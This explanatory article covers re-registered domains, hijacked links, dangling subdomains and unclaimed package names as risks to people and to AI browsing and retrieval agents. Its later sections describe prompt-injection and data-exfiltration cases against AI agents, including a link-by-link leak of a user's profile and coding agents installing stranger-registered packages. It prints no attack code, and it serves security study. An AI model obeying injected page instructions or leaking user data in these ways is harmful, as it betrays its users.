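# Re-registered domains and hijacked links as a risk to browsing agents and retrieval-augmented systems

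## How a domain changes hands and how AI systems read the web

A re-registered domain is an internet address that one party let lapse and another then registered. Links to the old site remain in other web pages, bookmarks, software and search indexes, so the new owner receives visitors who were looking for the old site. This is a familiar security problem for people and ordinary software. AI systems that open pages, search the web or cite sources follow the same links. Whether they run the same risk depends on the rules for how a domain changes owners and on how a page's text reaches a language model.

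### Names, registries and records

A domain name, such as wikipedia.org, is a readable substitute for a computer's numerical address. The Domain Name System (DNS) translates the name into the address whenever a browser or other program opens a page. The last part of the name is the top-level domain. Generic endings such as .com and .org come under the Internet Corporation for Assigned Names and Numbers (ICANN), a not-for-profit body that coordinates names worldwide. Country-code endings such as .uk and .de belong to national authorities.

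ICANN's *Acronyms and Terms* distinguishes the parties to a registration. The registrant is the person or organisation that wants the name. The registrar takes the order and passes it to the registry operator, which keeps the master database for a top-level domain (Verisign for .com). The registrant pays for one or more years at a time and must renew to keep the name. The name also needs DNS records, which point it to a web server and a mail server. ICANN's *Domain Name Industry* calls the companies that manage these records DNS hosts, and many registrars also do this work. A DNS record can be wrong even when the registration is in order.

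Each registration has a public record showing its creation date, expiry date and registrar. WHOIS was long the service for looking up these records, but the Registration Data Access Protocol (RDAP) replaced it as the definitive source for generic domains on 28 January 2025, according to ICANN's *Launching RDAP; Sunsetting WHOIS* (2025). The records also used to give the owner's name and contact details, but privacy rules have since removed many of these fields, as Muzammil, Ansari and colleagues note in *Echoes of the Past* (2026). An outsider can therefore usually learn when the current registration began but not who holds it.

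### From expiry to release

Suppose that a college lecturer runs a site of programming tutorials at pythonporch.example. (Nobody can register names under .example, so read it as a .com.) Over ten years the site has gathered links from a university reading list and from answers on programming forums, and one popular tutorial tells beginners which software package to install. The lecturer retires, the payment card on file runs out, and the registration expires on 1 March. If the registrar uses the full periods, the calendar looks like this:

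| Stage | Usual length | Dates | Who can claim the name | What a visitor finds |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Auto-renew grace period | 30 to 45 days | 1 March to 15 April | The lecturer, by renewing | Often the old site; at the end an expiry notice or nothing |
| Redemption period | 30 days | 15 April to 15 May | The lecturer, usually at a higher price | Nothing |
| Pending delete | 5 days | 15 to 20 May | Nobody | Nothing |
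| Public release | | From 20 May | Anyone | Whatever the new owner puts there |

The first stage is named for the registry's automatic one-year renewal of a domain on its expiry date. The registrar then has up to 45 days to cancel without owing the fee. If it cancels, the domain enters redemption. In *WHOIS Lost in Translation*, Lauinger, Onarlioglu and colleagues (2016) call the resulting 80 days the most common course, and *Domain Lifecycle*, a page from Nominet, which runs .uk, lists the same three periods for generic domain names. But Lauinger and colleagues also warn against treating 80 days as fixed. Registrars may delete a domain at any time after it expires, and ICANN's summary of public comments, *PSR on Expired Domain Deletion and Expired Registration Recovery Policies* (2025), gives a grace period of 0 to 45 days. With no grace period, anyone could register the lecturer's domain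 after 35 days.

ICANN's *Expired Registration Recovery Policy* requires registrars to send the owner two notices before a domain expires, about a month and about a week ahead, and a third within five days after expiry if the domain has been neither renewed nor deleted. In the example, all three go to a college mailbox that closed when the lecturer retired. Owners whose only contact address is on the expiring domain can also miss notices, because their email stops working along with their website, so ICANN recommends a second address.

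Visitors get much less warning. If a name is deleted eight days or more after it expires, the registrar must take the existing site offline for at least the last eight days in which the owner can still renew, as far as the registry permits. The tutorials could therefore stay online until 7 April, more than five weeks after the registration expired. The address would then stop working for at least 43 days. Someone who tried the link during that time would see that something was wrong, but a program that fetched the page in February and again in June would find a working site both times.

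Some names never go through this outage. ICANN's *5 Things every Domain Name Registrant should know* warns owners that during the grace period a registrar may auction the name to a third party if its terms of service allow it. *Game of Registrars*, a 2017 study of what happens to names after expiry, also describes registrars selling their customers' expired names before release. Such a sale can keep the name working throughout, and it usually leaves the original creation date in the record. Strictly speaking, the name never lapsed, because it was never open for anyone to register. A visitor following an old link still reaches a name under new control, but without the outage that might have revealed the change.

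It is unclear how common this route is. The .com registry alone was deleting between 66,000 and 112,000 names a day in early 2018. In the comments that ICANN collected, however, the arbitration centre of the World Intellectual Property Organization (WIPO) suggested that names rarely seem to reach expiration or deletion. That can hardly be true of names in general, but it may well be true of the valuable ones, which are the ones that end up in disputes.

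Country-code domains follow their own rules. Some have shorter recovery windows and some have none, according to an August 2026 report on expired names by the network-security company Infoblox. The calendar above is therefore not reliable for a tutorial site under .uk or .de.

### Dropcatching

Dropcatching means registering a name the moment the registry releases it. Lauinger, Buyukkayhan and colleagues (2018) studied how this works for .com in *From Deletion to Re-Registration in Zero Seconds*. The registry starts releasing names at 2 p.m. US Eastern Time each day and takes about an hour. The order is predictable, and the researchers closely reproduced it by sorting the names by when they were last updated. They found that 9.5% of the deleted names were re-registered with a delay of zero seconds.

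No person can do that by hand, so customers place a backorder with a specialised service, which floods the registry with requests around the expected second. At some registrars tied to these services, as few as 0.05% of the requests succeed. A service with more registrar accreditations can send more requests, and three large services held 75% of all accreditations in the group's earlier work. If several customers want the same name, the service may auction it among them.

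Many buyers have no bad intent. Investors hold names for resale, and security researchers register some to keep others from getting them. Infoblox once failed to renew a domain it used internally. The new owner asked for $40,000 to return it and now asks for more than $52,000.

However, an attacker does not have to beat dropcatchers to a name. Backorders cost two to ten times as much as an ordinary registration, and most deleted names go unregistered on the day they are released. Miramirkhani and colleagues, in *Domains Do Change Their Spots* (2022), therefore chose names that dropcatchers had passed over and registered 201 of them for $1,464.64, or about seven dollars each.

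In the example, no service bids for pythonporch.example, and three days after its release a stranger registers it at the ordinary price. The stranger restores the old tutorials from a web archive and changes only the line that names the package beginners should install. From 15 to 23 May the name was first in its final days of deletion and then a lapsed domain, which anyone could register. It is now a re-registered domain. The entry on the university's reading list has become a hijacked link, because it leads to someone the list's author never meant to recommend. The visitors who keep coming, and the reputation that brings them, are the domain's residual trust.

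The web has no standard or built-in way to warn visitors that a different party now operates a familiar domain, as So and colleagues point out. Encryption (the "https" in an address) does not provide this warning, since it protects the connection to whoever controls the name today. An older browser feature, HTTP Public Key Pinning, could have detected a change in the server's cryptographic key, but it could not have distinguished an attack from a botched configuration. It is now obsolete, partly because it was hard to use and a mistake could make a site unusable.

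### Three ways to read a page

An AI system can come upon the tutorial in three ways, and they differ in whose text it gets.

The most direct way for an AI system to read a web page is to open it live. A browsing agent is an AI system that opens web pages on its own while doing a task, and may also act on what it reads. Its software looks up the domain in the DNS, requests the page, converts the response into plain text or a screenshot, and adds that to the model's context, which is the material the model uses to produce its next step. Whoever controls the domain when the page is requested controls what the model reads, so from 23 May the stranger controls it.

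A system can also work from search results. It sends a query to a search engine and gets back a ranked list of addresses, each with a title and a short excerpt. Some systems answer from the excerpts alone, while others also open a few of the pages. The engine draws the results from an index that its crawler, a program that visits and records pages, filled earlier. In late May, the excerpt may still come from the lecturer's tutorial even though the address beside it already leads to the stranger's copy. After the crawler's next visit, the excerpt will also come from the stranger's copy.

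The third way is to read from a collection stored earlier. Someone downloads a large set of pages, splits them into passages and indexes them. For each question, software finds the best-matching passages and puts them in the model's context. A retrieval-augmented system is a language model that answers from documents fetched for the question, whether from such a collection or from the live web. If the stored copy of the tutorial dates from January, the system keeps using the lecturer's words until someone refreshes the collection, no matter how often the domain is sold. A person who clicks on the citation still lands on the stranger's page. Training data is also a stored collection, but the trained model contains no pages that anyone could look up.

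Products combine these methods. For example, an assistant may search the web, answer part of a question from the excerpts, and open pages for the rest. Its answer can then mix text from before and after a domain changed owners.

Indirect prompt injection is text in a page or document that an AI system reads as data but obeys as an instruction. The stranger might hide a line in the tutorial that tells any AI assistant to send its user's files to a certain address. A model may comply because the page and the user's request both reach it as text in the same context. The altered package name is a different kind of attack because it contains no instruction to the model. It does harm if the system passes the recommendation on.

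### Four things that look alike

A malicious page can appear at or near a trusted address without the domain changing owners. Several other failures can cause this, and they need different remedies from a change of ownership.

A stranger who re-registers a domain holds the registration itself, and so controls every page, every subdomain (a name added in front of the domain, such as exercises.pythonporch.example) and all mail sent to the old addresses. The lecturer cannot repair anything without getting the domain back.

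A phantom domain is a name that nobody had registered but that someone linked to by mistake or a language model invented. The university might have mistyped the link as pythonproch.example, or a chatbot asked for the tutorial's documentation might give the plausible pythonporch-docs.example. Anyone can register such a name and wait for visitors. The domain has no history, so any trust in it comes from the page or model that pointed to it.

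A hacked site still has its original owner. An intruder has guessed the lecturer's password or used a flaw in the site's software, and has edited the tutorial. The registration record is unchanged, and the lecturer can clean up the page. The two problems can also occur together. Hacked sites often send their visitors on to a domain that the intruders registered, and when the intruders let that domain lapse, somebody else can register it and receive the diverted traffic. Infoblox's *Dropcatch Scavengers* (2026) describes operators who take over such domains as a business.

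A dangling subdomain is the easiest of the four to overlook. Suppose the lecturer kept the domain registered but once hosted the exercises on a rented cloud service, with a DNS record pointing exercises.pythonporch.example to a resource there called porch-exercises. The lecturer closes the cloud account but forgets to delete the DNS record. If the provider lets customers choose such names freely, a stranger can open an account, claim porch-exercises and serve pages under the lecturer's domain, even though the lecturer's registration is still current.

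Earlier research had counted many vulnerable records of this kind without showing that anyone exploited them. *Cloudy with a Chance of Cyberattacks* (Frieß, Gattermayer and colleagues, 2024) tracked cloud-hosted domains and subdomains for three years, 3.1 million of them by the end, and found 20,904 actual hijacks. A third lasted more than 65 days. The attackers kept to resources whose names they could enter themselves, as in the example. The study found no cases in which an attacker obtained a released numerical address from the provider's large random pool, the type of takeover that earlier work had concentrated on. Three quarters of the abuse served to raise the attackers' own pages in search rankings, which is also a way into any AI system that starts from search results.

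*Dangling DNS* (Bachu, 2026) describes a further scenario based on the same weakness, in which an employee asks an AI agent to summarise a page on a forgotten company subdomain that an attacker has claimed. The page contains hidden instructions to summarise internal documents as well, and the agent writes the summary into a page that the attacker controls. The attack works only if the agent can reach the internal documents, follows the hidden instructions and writes its output back into the page. The post appeared on the site of Akamai, which sells a tool for finding dangling records, and reports no real case of the attack.

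## What re-registered domains do to human visitors and ordinary software

An old link is a danger only if someone still follows it. To count who does, So and colleagues put an almost empty page on each of the 201 cheap domains they had registered for *Domains Do Change Their Spots* and recorded all requests between 1 August and 1 December 2019. They received 650,737,621 requests from 5,540,379 IP addresses (the numerical addresses from which devices connect to the internet). That total proves little on its own, because any computer on the public internet receives a constant stream of automated probes. The study's value depends on how well it separated these probes from requests by people and programs that wanted the old site.

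### Which domains the researchers bought

The group wanted to know what a buyer with little money and no particular target could get. It therefore checked how often computers had looked up each domain in the DNS while it was still active, using counts from a commercial archive. It ignored the qualities that investors pay for, such as a short name.

The researchers first ran two small trials. In June 2019 they set up ten expired domains with many past lookups, ten with few, and ten servers with no domain, and logged web requests for a week. The domains with few past lookups drew about as much traffic as the servers with no domain. Two of the domains with many past lookups drew more than twice as much as any server in the other groups. In the other trial, every sampled domain with more than a million lookups before expiry received at least 10,000 lookups in the two weeks after someone re-registered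 it. The researchers then set a million lookups as their threshold for buying a domain.

The main round, in August 2019, produced 550 candidates. The researchers discarded 321 as near-duplicates of other names on the list and lost 57 to other buyers. They registered the remaining 172, adding them to 29 from a pilot. Three in four of the names they tried to get were still available at the ordinary price.

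Each domain had its own server and IP address, and its DNS records also sent requests for any subdomain to that server. The servers answered every web request with a "page not found" notice. They also recorded attempts to log in through SSH, Telnet and FTP, which are used for remote access and file transfer.

### Separating visitors from scanners

To identify background noise, the researchers ran 52 placebo servers that had no domain but used the same range of IP addresses and offered the same services. Nobody could reach a placebo by following a link, so anything that contacted one was scanning the network. The researchers marked every IP address that did so as a bot, and kept that label when the address visited one of the 201 domains.

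The error page contained bot traps, which were links hidden from people in one-pixel-wide images, in comments in the page's code, and in elements that the page hid or removed as it loaded. An ordinary browser has no reason to request these links, but a program that collects every link may do so. The traps caught only about 43% of the addresses that identified themselves as bots.

The page also ran a fingerprinting script, which sent back details such as the visitor's screen and installed fonts. If a request was labelled as coming from a major browser but no fingerprint followed, the researchers marked the address as a bot, because most bots did not run such scripts. They treated a fingerprint as evidence that the visitor was not a bot. They did not apply this test to software that did not identify itself as a browser, such as a file-sharing program.

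The researchers also marked addresses as bots if they tried known exploits, searched for backup files or appeared on published blocklists. The blocklists flagged about 1.87 million addresses. All the other filters together flagged about 417,000, and four fifths of those were also on the blocklists. The researchers had no list of known humans and bots to check the filters against, so they took this overlap as a sign that the filters were sound.

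The best evidence of a real visitor was a request for a specific page that used to exist, such as an old article the visitor had bookmarked, because a scanner is unlikely to guess its address. The researchers used a web archive to list the old sites' former pages.

Any address with a bot mark was classed as a bot. Of the rest, those with at least one mark in their favour counted as "trust" and those with none as "neutral". The rule is severe because many people can share one IP address, so one infected laptop could get a whole office classed as a bot. It would also exclude an AI agent that behaved like a crawler from the trust count. The trust figure is therefore meant as a minimum.

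### What still contacted the old domains

Of the IP addresses that made web requests, 50.58% were classified as trust, 43.59% as bot and 5.82% as neutral. No address that used SSH or Telnet was classified as trust, and the only FTP address that was turned out to be a false positive.

It would be easy to conclude from the 50.58% that half the visitors to a typical expired domain are looking for its old owner. In fact more than 95% of the domains received over 95% bot traffic, and only 7% of them had a trust share above 1%. A handful of very busy domains produced the overall figure:

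| Former use of the domain | Web requests | IP addresses | Share marked trust |
|---|---|---|---|
| Torrent tracker | 138 million | 2.5 million | 79% |
| Control server for malware | 55 million | 1.3 million | 28% |
| Service behind an Android library | 23 million | 683,000 | 39% |
| Sports news site | 13 million | 133,000 | 16% |
| Statistics on college computer labs | 144 million | 52,000 | 87% |

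A torrent tracker tells file-sharing programs which other computers hold the file they want. This one received about seven million requests a day until it overloaded the researchers' system, and they then left it offline. By the paper's numbers, the tracker accounts for roughly three quarters of all the trust addresses in the study, and the malware server and the Android library account for nearly all the rest. Most of this "trust" therefore came from programs that were still contacting an address someone had written into them.

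The Android case shows how hard such an address can be to trace. Unrelated apps, one with more than 500,000 downloads, had included the library to control the phone's vibration. Their users had no reason to know that the apps were sending data to a company called Avant Mobile, or that its domain had expired. The researchers worked this out by taking old apps apart, then running them on a simulated phone and watching which domains they looked up.

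The sports news site, with about 21,000 trust addresses, is the clearest example of a domain with human visitors. Its trust traffic died away less than a month after the researchers took over, while traffic to the Android and computer-lab domains stayed steady. Readers presumably noticed the error page and stopped visiting, whereas a program keeps sending requests until someone updates it.

People can also depend on a lapsed domain without visiting it. One of the 201 domains had supplied a script to several cryptocurrency news sites. At least one of these sites, forklog.media, still included the script in February 2020, more than six months after the researchers had re-registered the domain. A hostile owner could have used the domain to run code in the browsers of that site's readers.

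So and colleagues did not test what such an owner could achieve. They sent visitors only the error page and its scripts, so the study shows who made contact but not what those clients would have accepted in reply. They also sampled domains with unusually busy pasts, so the results cannot be generalized to all expired domains.

### Links to domains that nobody ever owned

A link can also be open to hijacking if it points to a "phantom domain", one that has never been registered. Saric and colleagues searched large crawls of the web and found links to more than 572,000 phantom domains under .com, according to the abstract of their study *Hyperlink Hijacking*, reprinted in *Exploiting Mistyped URLs* (Schneier, 2024).

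The researchers traced the links to 17 common mistakes by web publishers. Most are simple typing errors, according to their article in The Conversation, *We analysed the entire web and found a cybersecurity threat*. Other faulty links come from website templates, when a designer uses a made-up address as a placeholder and nobody replaces it after a customer installs the template. The faulty links appeared on the sites of governments and financial firms, and in software for enforcing privacy law on websites.

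Saric and colleagues then registered 51 of the phantom domains and compared their traffic with that of similar new domains that had no faulty links pointing to them. Of the 51, 88% drew more traffic than the control, and the busiest drew up to ten times as much. This is good evidence that mistaken links alone can bring traffic.

The number of people behind that traffic is less clear. Ten times the traffic of an obscure new domain may still be modest, since little-used domains in So and colleagues' first trial received hardly more than background noise. The researchers also only observed traffic and did not imitate the sites that visitors were looking for, so they could not learn how many would have been fooled. The count covers only .com domains.

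A reader commenting under Schneier's post doubted that the problem matters much in everyday life, since criminals would have bought these names long ago if there were money in them. That is a fair point, but the count of phantom domains can't show whether it is right, because the count leaves out any that criminals have already registered.

### How many re-registered domains turn malicious

In both experiments the researchers bought the domains themselves, so neither shows how common hostile re-registration is. Muzammil and colleagues studied other people's purchases. Their system, EchoLoc, read a continuous feed of registration records for 32 days, from 11 July to 12 August 2025. It counted a newly registered domain as re-registered if an older creation date was on file. It found 1.5 million re-registered domains, or about 46,600 a day.

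Infoblox, which supplied the data for EchoLoc, published similar numbers for the first half of 2026. It counted an average of 50,400 re-registrations a day under generic endings such as .com, and around 65,000 including country-code domains. It estimates that nearly one in five new registrations is for a previously owned name.

The EchoLoc paper gives a much smaller share, about 1%, because it divides the 1.5 million by 144.6 million new registrations. That total would mean 4.5 million new domains a day, whereas Infoblox's figures imply about 250,000 under generic endings. The 144.6 million probably includes many records that are not new domains. The daily counts of re-registrations are much closer to each other, but they come from the same company, so they are not independent evidence.

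Both counts omit names that registrars auction before release, since these normally keep their creation date. Many country-code registries publish no creation dates. EchoLoc may also overcount, because it treats any domain registered again after deletion as having a new owner. Muzammil and colleagues argue that the old owner is rarely the one who registers it again, having already had several chances to renew.

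Many of these domains had little residual trust to pass on. More than half of the re-registered domains were first registered in 2023 or later, and over 210,000 had been re-registered at least twice. Infoblox tried to determine how many buyers use their domains and how many hold them for resale, but the records were too ambiguous.

Muzammil and colleagues used Infoblox's DNS traffic to find which domains were still in use. Infoblox's customers, which are organisations with many employees and devices each, had looked up 66,000 of the 1.5 million domains (about 4%) after re-registration. The researchers classed 9,171 of these (13.9%) as malicious. Infoblox had already listed more than half of the malicious domains as known threats, and EchoLoc's page classifier found the other 3,841.

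Gambling accounted for 3,039 of the newly found sites, adult content for 312 and scams for 308. The paper gives no such breakdown for the sites Infoblox already knew about. "Malicious" is a broad label here, because the classifier treats gambling itself as a high-risk category. A page that only advertises betting is a nuisance to someone looking for the old site, but it does not attack their computer.

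Some of the examples are worse than a nuisance. A golf club's domain, first registered in 1998, now offers a modified slot-machine app that bypasses the official app stores' checks. Another domain, codinggear.blog, used to host programming tutorials, much like the lecturer's site. It now sends visitors through an advertising tracker to a changing set of adult sites, and 195 customer organisations had looked it up. Anyone who wanted a tutorial would see at once that something was wrong. None of the paper's examples resembles the lecturer's case, in which the old site was copied with one line altered.

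### Most of the traffic goes to a few names

About 80% of the newly found malicious domains received about 100 DNS queries or fewer each. The most queried, netdna-ssl.com, received 2,251,878, about five times as many as the next domain. Those queries came from 1,121 organisations and were for 15,225 different names under the domain.

The reason is that the domain used to belong to a content delivery network, a service that stores images, style sheets and scripts for other websites and sends them to readers from nearby servers. Web pages all over the internet contain its addresses, so a reader's browser contacts the domain without the reader clicking on anything. After the domain changed owners, it redirected to a site for unauthorised downloads from a social media platform. A page that requests a style sheet and receives that site instead may just look broken, but an owner in the same position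 could return a working script of their own, and the page would run it.

The paper gives 24 July 2025 as the date the domain expired, but this is probably the date it was re-registered. A .com name isn't released until at least 35 days after it expires, and the study ended just 19 days after 24 July, on 12 August.

The 2.25 million queries, however, include traffic from before re-registration, when the domain still served its original purpose, so they are not a count of visits to the new owner. A DNS query also shows only that a computer looked up a domain's address, not whether a person or a program made the request or whether anything harmful loaded afterwards. The data come from Infoblox's corporate customers, so they may not reflect home use or regions where the company has few clients.

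### What hostile buyers spend

So and colleagues showed that a domain that already has visitors can cost about seven dollars. Some criminals pay far more. Infoblox's *$7 Million in Expired Domains Fuel a Streaming Empire* (2026) describes a group that the company calls Sable Squirrel, which controls more than 10,000 domains. Most of them carry pirated football streams that lead viewers to betting sites. Infoblox could price about 160 of the group's expired domains individually, for a total of more than $430,000, or an average of around $2,700.

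The $7 million in the title is an extrapolation from those 160 domains to the rest of the group's expired domains. It holds only if the 160 are typical, and domains whose prices outsiders can find may well be more expensive than the rest. The confirmed sum still shows that a criminal business will pay market prices for the residual trust in expired domains.

For that price the group gets links from other sites, existing visitors and a long registration history, which some security filters treat as a sign that a domain is trustworthy. One of its purchases, healthymagination.com, once belonged to a General Electric health initiative. Another, veinteractive.com, belonged to a British advertising technology company that collapsed in 2017, and thousands of other websites still contact it every day. Of the domains whose purchase Infoblox could date, the group put 24% to use on the day it bought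 them and 94% within two weeks.

From November 2025, the group also used some of these domains to control malware. Visitors to these sites see live football, while infected computers receive instructions from the same domains. Infoblox counted about 350 domains set up this way in December. This harm differs from that of a hijacked link because the infected computers contact the domain for instructions, not for the old site's content.

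Old links did lead directly to malware in a case involving another group, Shady Squirrel. A content delivery network's domain had expired after a larger company bought the start-up that used it. Major media websites still had addresses at that domain in their pages, and Infoblox reports that the requests went unanswered for years, apparently without anyone noticing. In February 2026 Shady Squirrel acquired the domain and began sending the sites' visitors to malware.

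This group is selective about whom it attacks. For example, Infoblox tested the group's tech-support scam on a research machine and found that it appeared only to people who arrived from a search engine on a Windows computer. Most visits ended at the original website. This selectivity makes victims hard to count, and Infoblox does not say how many people the February takeover infected.

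## How an abandoned address reaches an AI system

An AI system can reach an abandoned domain in four ways. A search engine may return the address, a page the system is reading may link to it, documentation written for AI agents may include it, or the language model may generate it without having read it during the task.

### Search results

A search engine ranks a page partly by the links that point to it, and those links stay in place when the domain lapses. The engine detects that a site is gone only when its crawler next visits, and even then it may keep the entry. So if someone asks an assistant about a Python error in late May, pythonporch.example may still appear near the top of the results, without the stranger who now owns the domain having had to break into the lecturer's server.

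The start-up AIR Security looked for such addresses and published its findings in October 2026 under the name "Web Hole". According to Lagonsin (2026), in *Web Hole attack targets AI agents via abandoned sites*, the company's researchers compiled about 2,000 queries that an AI agent might send in an ordinary session and examined roughly 6,500 sites. They found 36 sites that still appeared in the search results even though nobody held their domains and anyone could buy them. Antipov (2026), in *Домен умер, но поисковик о нём помнит* ("The domain died, but the search engine remembers it"), gives the queries that returned two of them. A query about a Python error returned pyquestions.com, and a question about a feature of AngularJS, a toolkit for building websites, returned thestackoverflow.com.

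Thirty-six in 6,500 is about one site in 180. One site can turn up for many queries and another for a single rare one, so this rate is not the chance that a given search goes wrong. AIR counted domains that an attacker could still register. It left out those that somebody had already re-registered, which are the only ones that can serve content to an agent.

The finding does show how long an index can hold on to a dead site. On the usual .com calendar, a site is offline for at least 35 days before the registry releases its name. If the two named domains followed that calendar, the search engine was still offering them after five weeks or more in which nobody could open them. (A dead site need not have been a good one, either. The name thestackoverflow.com looks like an imitation of Stack Overflow, the programming forum, so its visitors' trust may have been misplaced from the start.)

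Antipov describes how web pages reach Anthropic's assistant Claude. A tool called WebSearch returns addresses with short descriptions. If Claude needs more, a second tool, WebFetch, loads a chosen page, and a language model condenses the text before Claude receives it. The user may see the answer and the address but not the condensed text Claude received. No step checks who owns the domain.

AIR presents the attack as possible and offers no evidence of mass break-ins, as Antipov points out. A domain's ranking may also not survive the purchase, because the search engine can reassess the site once its crawler has visited the new owner's pages. A buyer who restores the old pages, as the stranger did with the tutorials, should have a better chance of keeping the ranking. AIR counted its 36 domains before anyone had bought them, so the count doesn't show whether rankings last after a sale. Lagonsin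 reports that AIR also describes a slower method with no change of owner, in which an attacker builds a useful site, waits for it to rank well and then changes the content.

A second AIR test, from November 2026, covered pages that were already live. Faisal (2026) reports in *Every Major Search API Fed AI Coding Agents Malicious Content, Benchmark Finds* that the firm sent 4,719 coding queries to eight search services that developers connect to their agents, including Brave, Exa and Perplexity, and received more than 282,000 results. In 534 of the searches, the results included content already known to be malicious, with rates ranging from 0.8% to 2.2% depending on the service. Re-registered domains are one of AIR's six categories of attack, but Faisal gives no separate number for them, so they could account for most of the malicious results or almost none.

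The queries in that test were less natural than Faisal's phrase "real coding queries" suggests. AIR started from recorded sessions of coding agents, kept the 850 that involved the most searching, and wrote 50 plausible searches for each. It has not released the queries or the scanner that judged the results. It also has a product to sell. The company emerged from stealth in September 2026 with $50 million in funding and a firewall for AI agents, according to *AI Agent Firewall Startup AIR Security Emerges From Stealth With $50 Million* (Townsend, 2026). These concerns matter more for the November test than for the October one, because outsiders cannot check a private scanner's verdicts, while anyone can look up whether pyquestions.com has an owner.

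The clearest cases of domains that had actually changed hands come from James Brockbank, managing director of the marketing agency Digitaloft, who asked ChatGPT in 2025 to recommend online casinos and then looked into the sites it cited. One site used the former domain of an arts charity that the BBC, CNN and Bloomberg had once linked to, according to TechRadar's *Criminals and scammers are using hacked websites and expired domain names*. Another used the former domain of a youth coalition affiliated with the United Nations. It promoted casinos "not on GamStop", which were likely to appeal to gamblers who had used that British scheme to bar themselves from betting sites.

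Some of Brockbank's other examples were hacked sites that still had their original owners. A law practice had casino pages buried in its website. A page about online slots on an American summer camp's site looked blank because the intruder had set white text on a white background. A program that extracts text can still read such words.

These cases show that ChatGPT has cited re-registered domains in its answers, but not how often. Search Engine Journal's *ChatGPT Recommendations Potentially Influenced By Hacked Sites* describes the work as personal testing rather than a comprehensive study, and Brockbank was searching in a trade where spam is common. The reason for the citations is also unclear. TechRadar attributes them to the domains' lingering reputation and a preference for recent content, but the text of a casino list might have been enough on its own. To find out, someone would have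 to publish the same list on a domain with no history and see whether ChatGPT cited it.

Google has listed "expired domain abuse" as spam in its search policies since March 2024. The term means buying an expired domain name mainly to exploit its ranking with content of little value to visitors. One of Google's examples is casino material on a former elementary school's site. The policy allows a buyer to put a worthwhile new site on an old name. It applies only to Google's results, and an assistant may draw on another index. The stranger's copy of the tutorials would be hard even for Google to classify, since nearly every line of it is useful.

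Netcraft's *Threat Actors are Finding Their Way into Your AI Summaries* cites a Fudan University study in which search engines with built-in language models filtered out 99.78% of traditional attempts to manipulate rankings. This is only weak evidence that they would filter out an old domain with its old text restored, which may not count as a traditional attempt.

### Links on pages the agent is already reading

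An agent can reach an abandoned address by following a link, without running a search. The university's reading list still links to pythonporch.example, and an agent may open that link if a student asks it to work through the list.

An agent can also load content from an abandoned domain without choosing to follow a link there. An agent that works through a full browser loads whatever the page's code requests, including scripts from other domains. If one of those domains has a new owner, as happened with the lapsed content delivery networks, the owner's script can rewrite the page before the model receives its text or a screenshot. A simpler tool that downloads the page without running scripts would not receive the altered text.

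Whether an agent may follow ordinary links depends on its tools. Willison (2026), in *163 posts tagged "prompt-injection"*, describes the rules for web_fetch, the tool that the chat version of Claude uses to open pages. Anthropic had restricted it to addresses that the user had typed or that the companion search tool had returned. The aim was to stop a hostile page from making Claude visit an address containing private data, which would send the data to the attacker.

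The restriction had a gap because the tool also accepted links inside pages it had already fetched. Ayush Paul, who found the gap, set up a site whose links spelled out the alphabet and told Claude to find its user's profile letter by letter. The sequence of links Claude opened revealed the user's name, home city and employer. Willison reported in July 2026 that Anthropic had since removed the tool's ability to follow links in fetched pages.

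Anthropic made this change to prevent data theft, but it also blocks most hijacked links. The tool can no longer open the old entry on the reading list unless the user pastes the address or a search returns it. Agents that control a browser or can run download commands on a computer may have no such limit.

Agents also encounter links in the files that tell them how to work. Ahmed (2026), in *Placeholder Domains Used by 349 AI Agent Skills Found Redirecting to Scams*, reports that Manifold Security found certain placeholder domains, written only as examples, in 359,000 files on GitHub and in 349 agent skills, which are packaged instructions for a particular task. The domains were redirecting visitors to scams, and Manifold observed the redirects on macOS. The domains also used cloaking, serving different content to different visitors from the same address.

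The first number counts files, many of which are presumably examples and tests that never contact the address. The 349 skills are more relevant because agents read them, but an agent may read a skill without visiting the address it mentions, and a scam aimed at Mac users may have no effect on an agent. The domains may also not be re-registered ones. Authors may have made up the names, in which case they were phantom domains until somebody noticed how many files contained them and registered them. Saric and colleagues found the same mistake in website templates.

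Hijacked pages can also link to one another. The casino list on the youth coalition's old domain had only one outside link, which led to another repurposed domain.

None of these accounts includes a count of the agents that arrived by this route. So and colleagues recorded who contacted their 201 domains in 2019, before browsing agents were in common use. Repeating their experiment with agents as a separate class of visitor would show how many now arrive through old links, and whether they keep returning after an error, as programs did, or stop, as readers of the sports news site apparently did.

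### Documentation written for agents

Some websites now publish files meant only for AI systems. Jeremy Howard, an AI researcher, proposed the llms.txt file in September 2024 as a short plain-text guide to a website, so that a language model would not have to pick out the important pages from the site's code. Some sites add a longer version, llms-full.txt. A software company's files may include the commands for installing its products.

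An install command typically names a package, which the computer downloads from a public registry and installs. The main registries are PyPI for Python and npm for JavaScript. An unclaimed package name, like an unclaimed domain, goes to whoever registers it first. If a company's documentation names a package that does not exist, a stranger can create it, and anyone who then follows the documentation will install the stranger's code.

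Alon Hertz, a researcher, looked for such gaps on 6,214 active domains belonging to large technology firms, defence contractors and Fortune 500 companies. He found 8,265 of the files, according to Heaton (2026) in *Your supplier's docs now tell your AI what to install*. Of these, 120 files, each on a different site, named packages or domains that nobody had registered. Those 120 files contained 227 install commands. TechRadar's *Top AI tools including Claude, Codex, and Hermes installed suspicious code* lists possible causes, including copying errors, packages that their makers had renamed or abandoned, and documentation that a language model had made up.

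Hertz then claimed some of the free names and published harmless packages under them that did nothing except contact his server when installed. The first contact came from a Fortune 500 company in less than an hour, and a few dozen more followed. The packages also recorded which program had started each installation. These programs were the coding agents Claude, OpenAI's Codex and Hermes, which is made by the AI company Nous Research.

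This is the strongest evidence for any of the four routes, because agents inside real companies ran code from package names that an outsider had only just claimed. But Hertz tested packages, not web pages. Someone who registered one of the unclaimed domains would still need an agent to open it and accept what it served. It is also unclear where the agents saw the package names. Hertz knows which program installed a package, but the name could have come from llms.txt, from the same command on an ordinary help page, or from the model's memory.

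A Japanese report, 三村 (2026), *AIエージェント向け「llms.txt」にサプライチェーンリスク* ("Supply-chain risk in llms.txt for AI agents"), gives slightly different figures: 8,565 files instead of 8,265, more than 237 unregistered references, and a first installation within four minutes. These differences don't change the result much. The report also mentions a malicious npm package in connection with Clerk, which makes login software. If that is right, someone other than Hertz has also noticed such gaps.

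In Hertz's experiment, the agent carried out a legitimate instruction from the company's own documentation, which meant readers to run the commands, but the name in the instruction led to a stranger's code. This was not prompt injection in the usual sense. The same distinction came up in an August 2026 post on Willison's site about a different attack. Johann Rehberger, a security researcher, had tricked Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, into unpacking an archive and running code that loaded a malicious file from it. By his account, the attack worked 80% of the time. A reader objected that the model had never obeyed a hostile instruction from the website. Willison agreed and described the attack as more of a "confused environment" attack.

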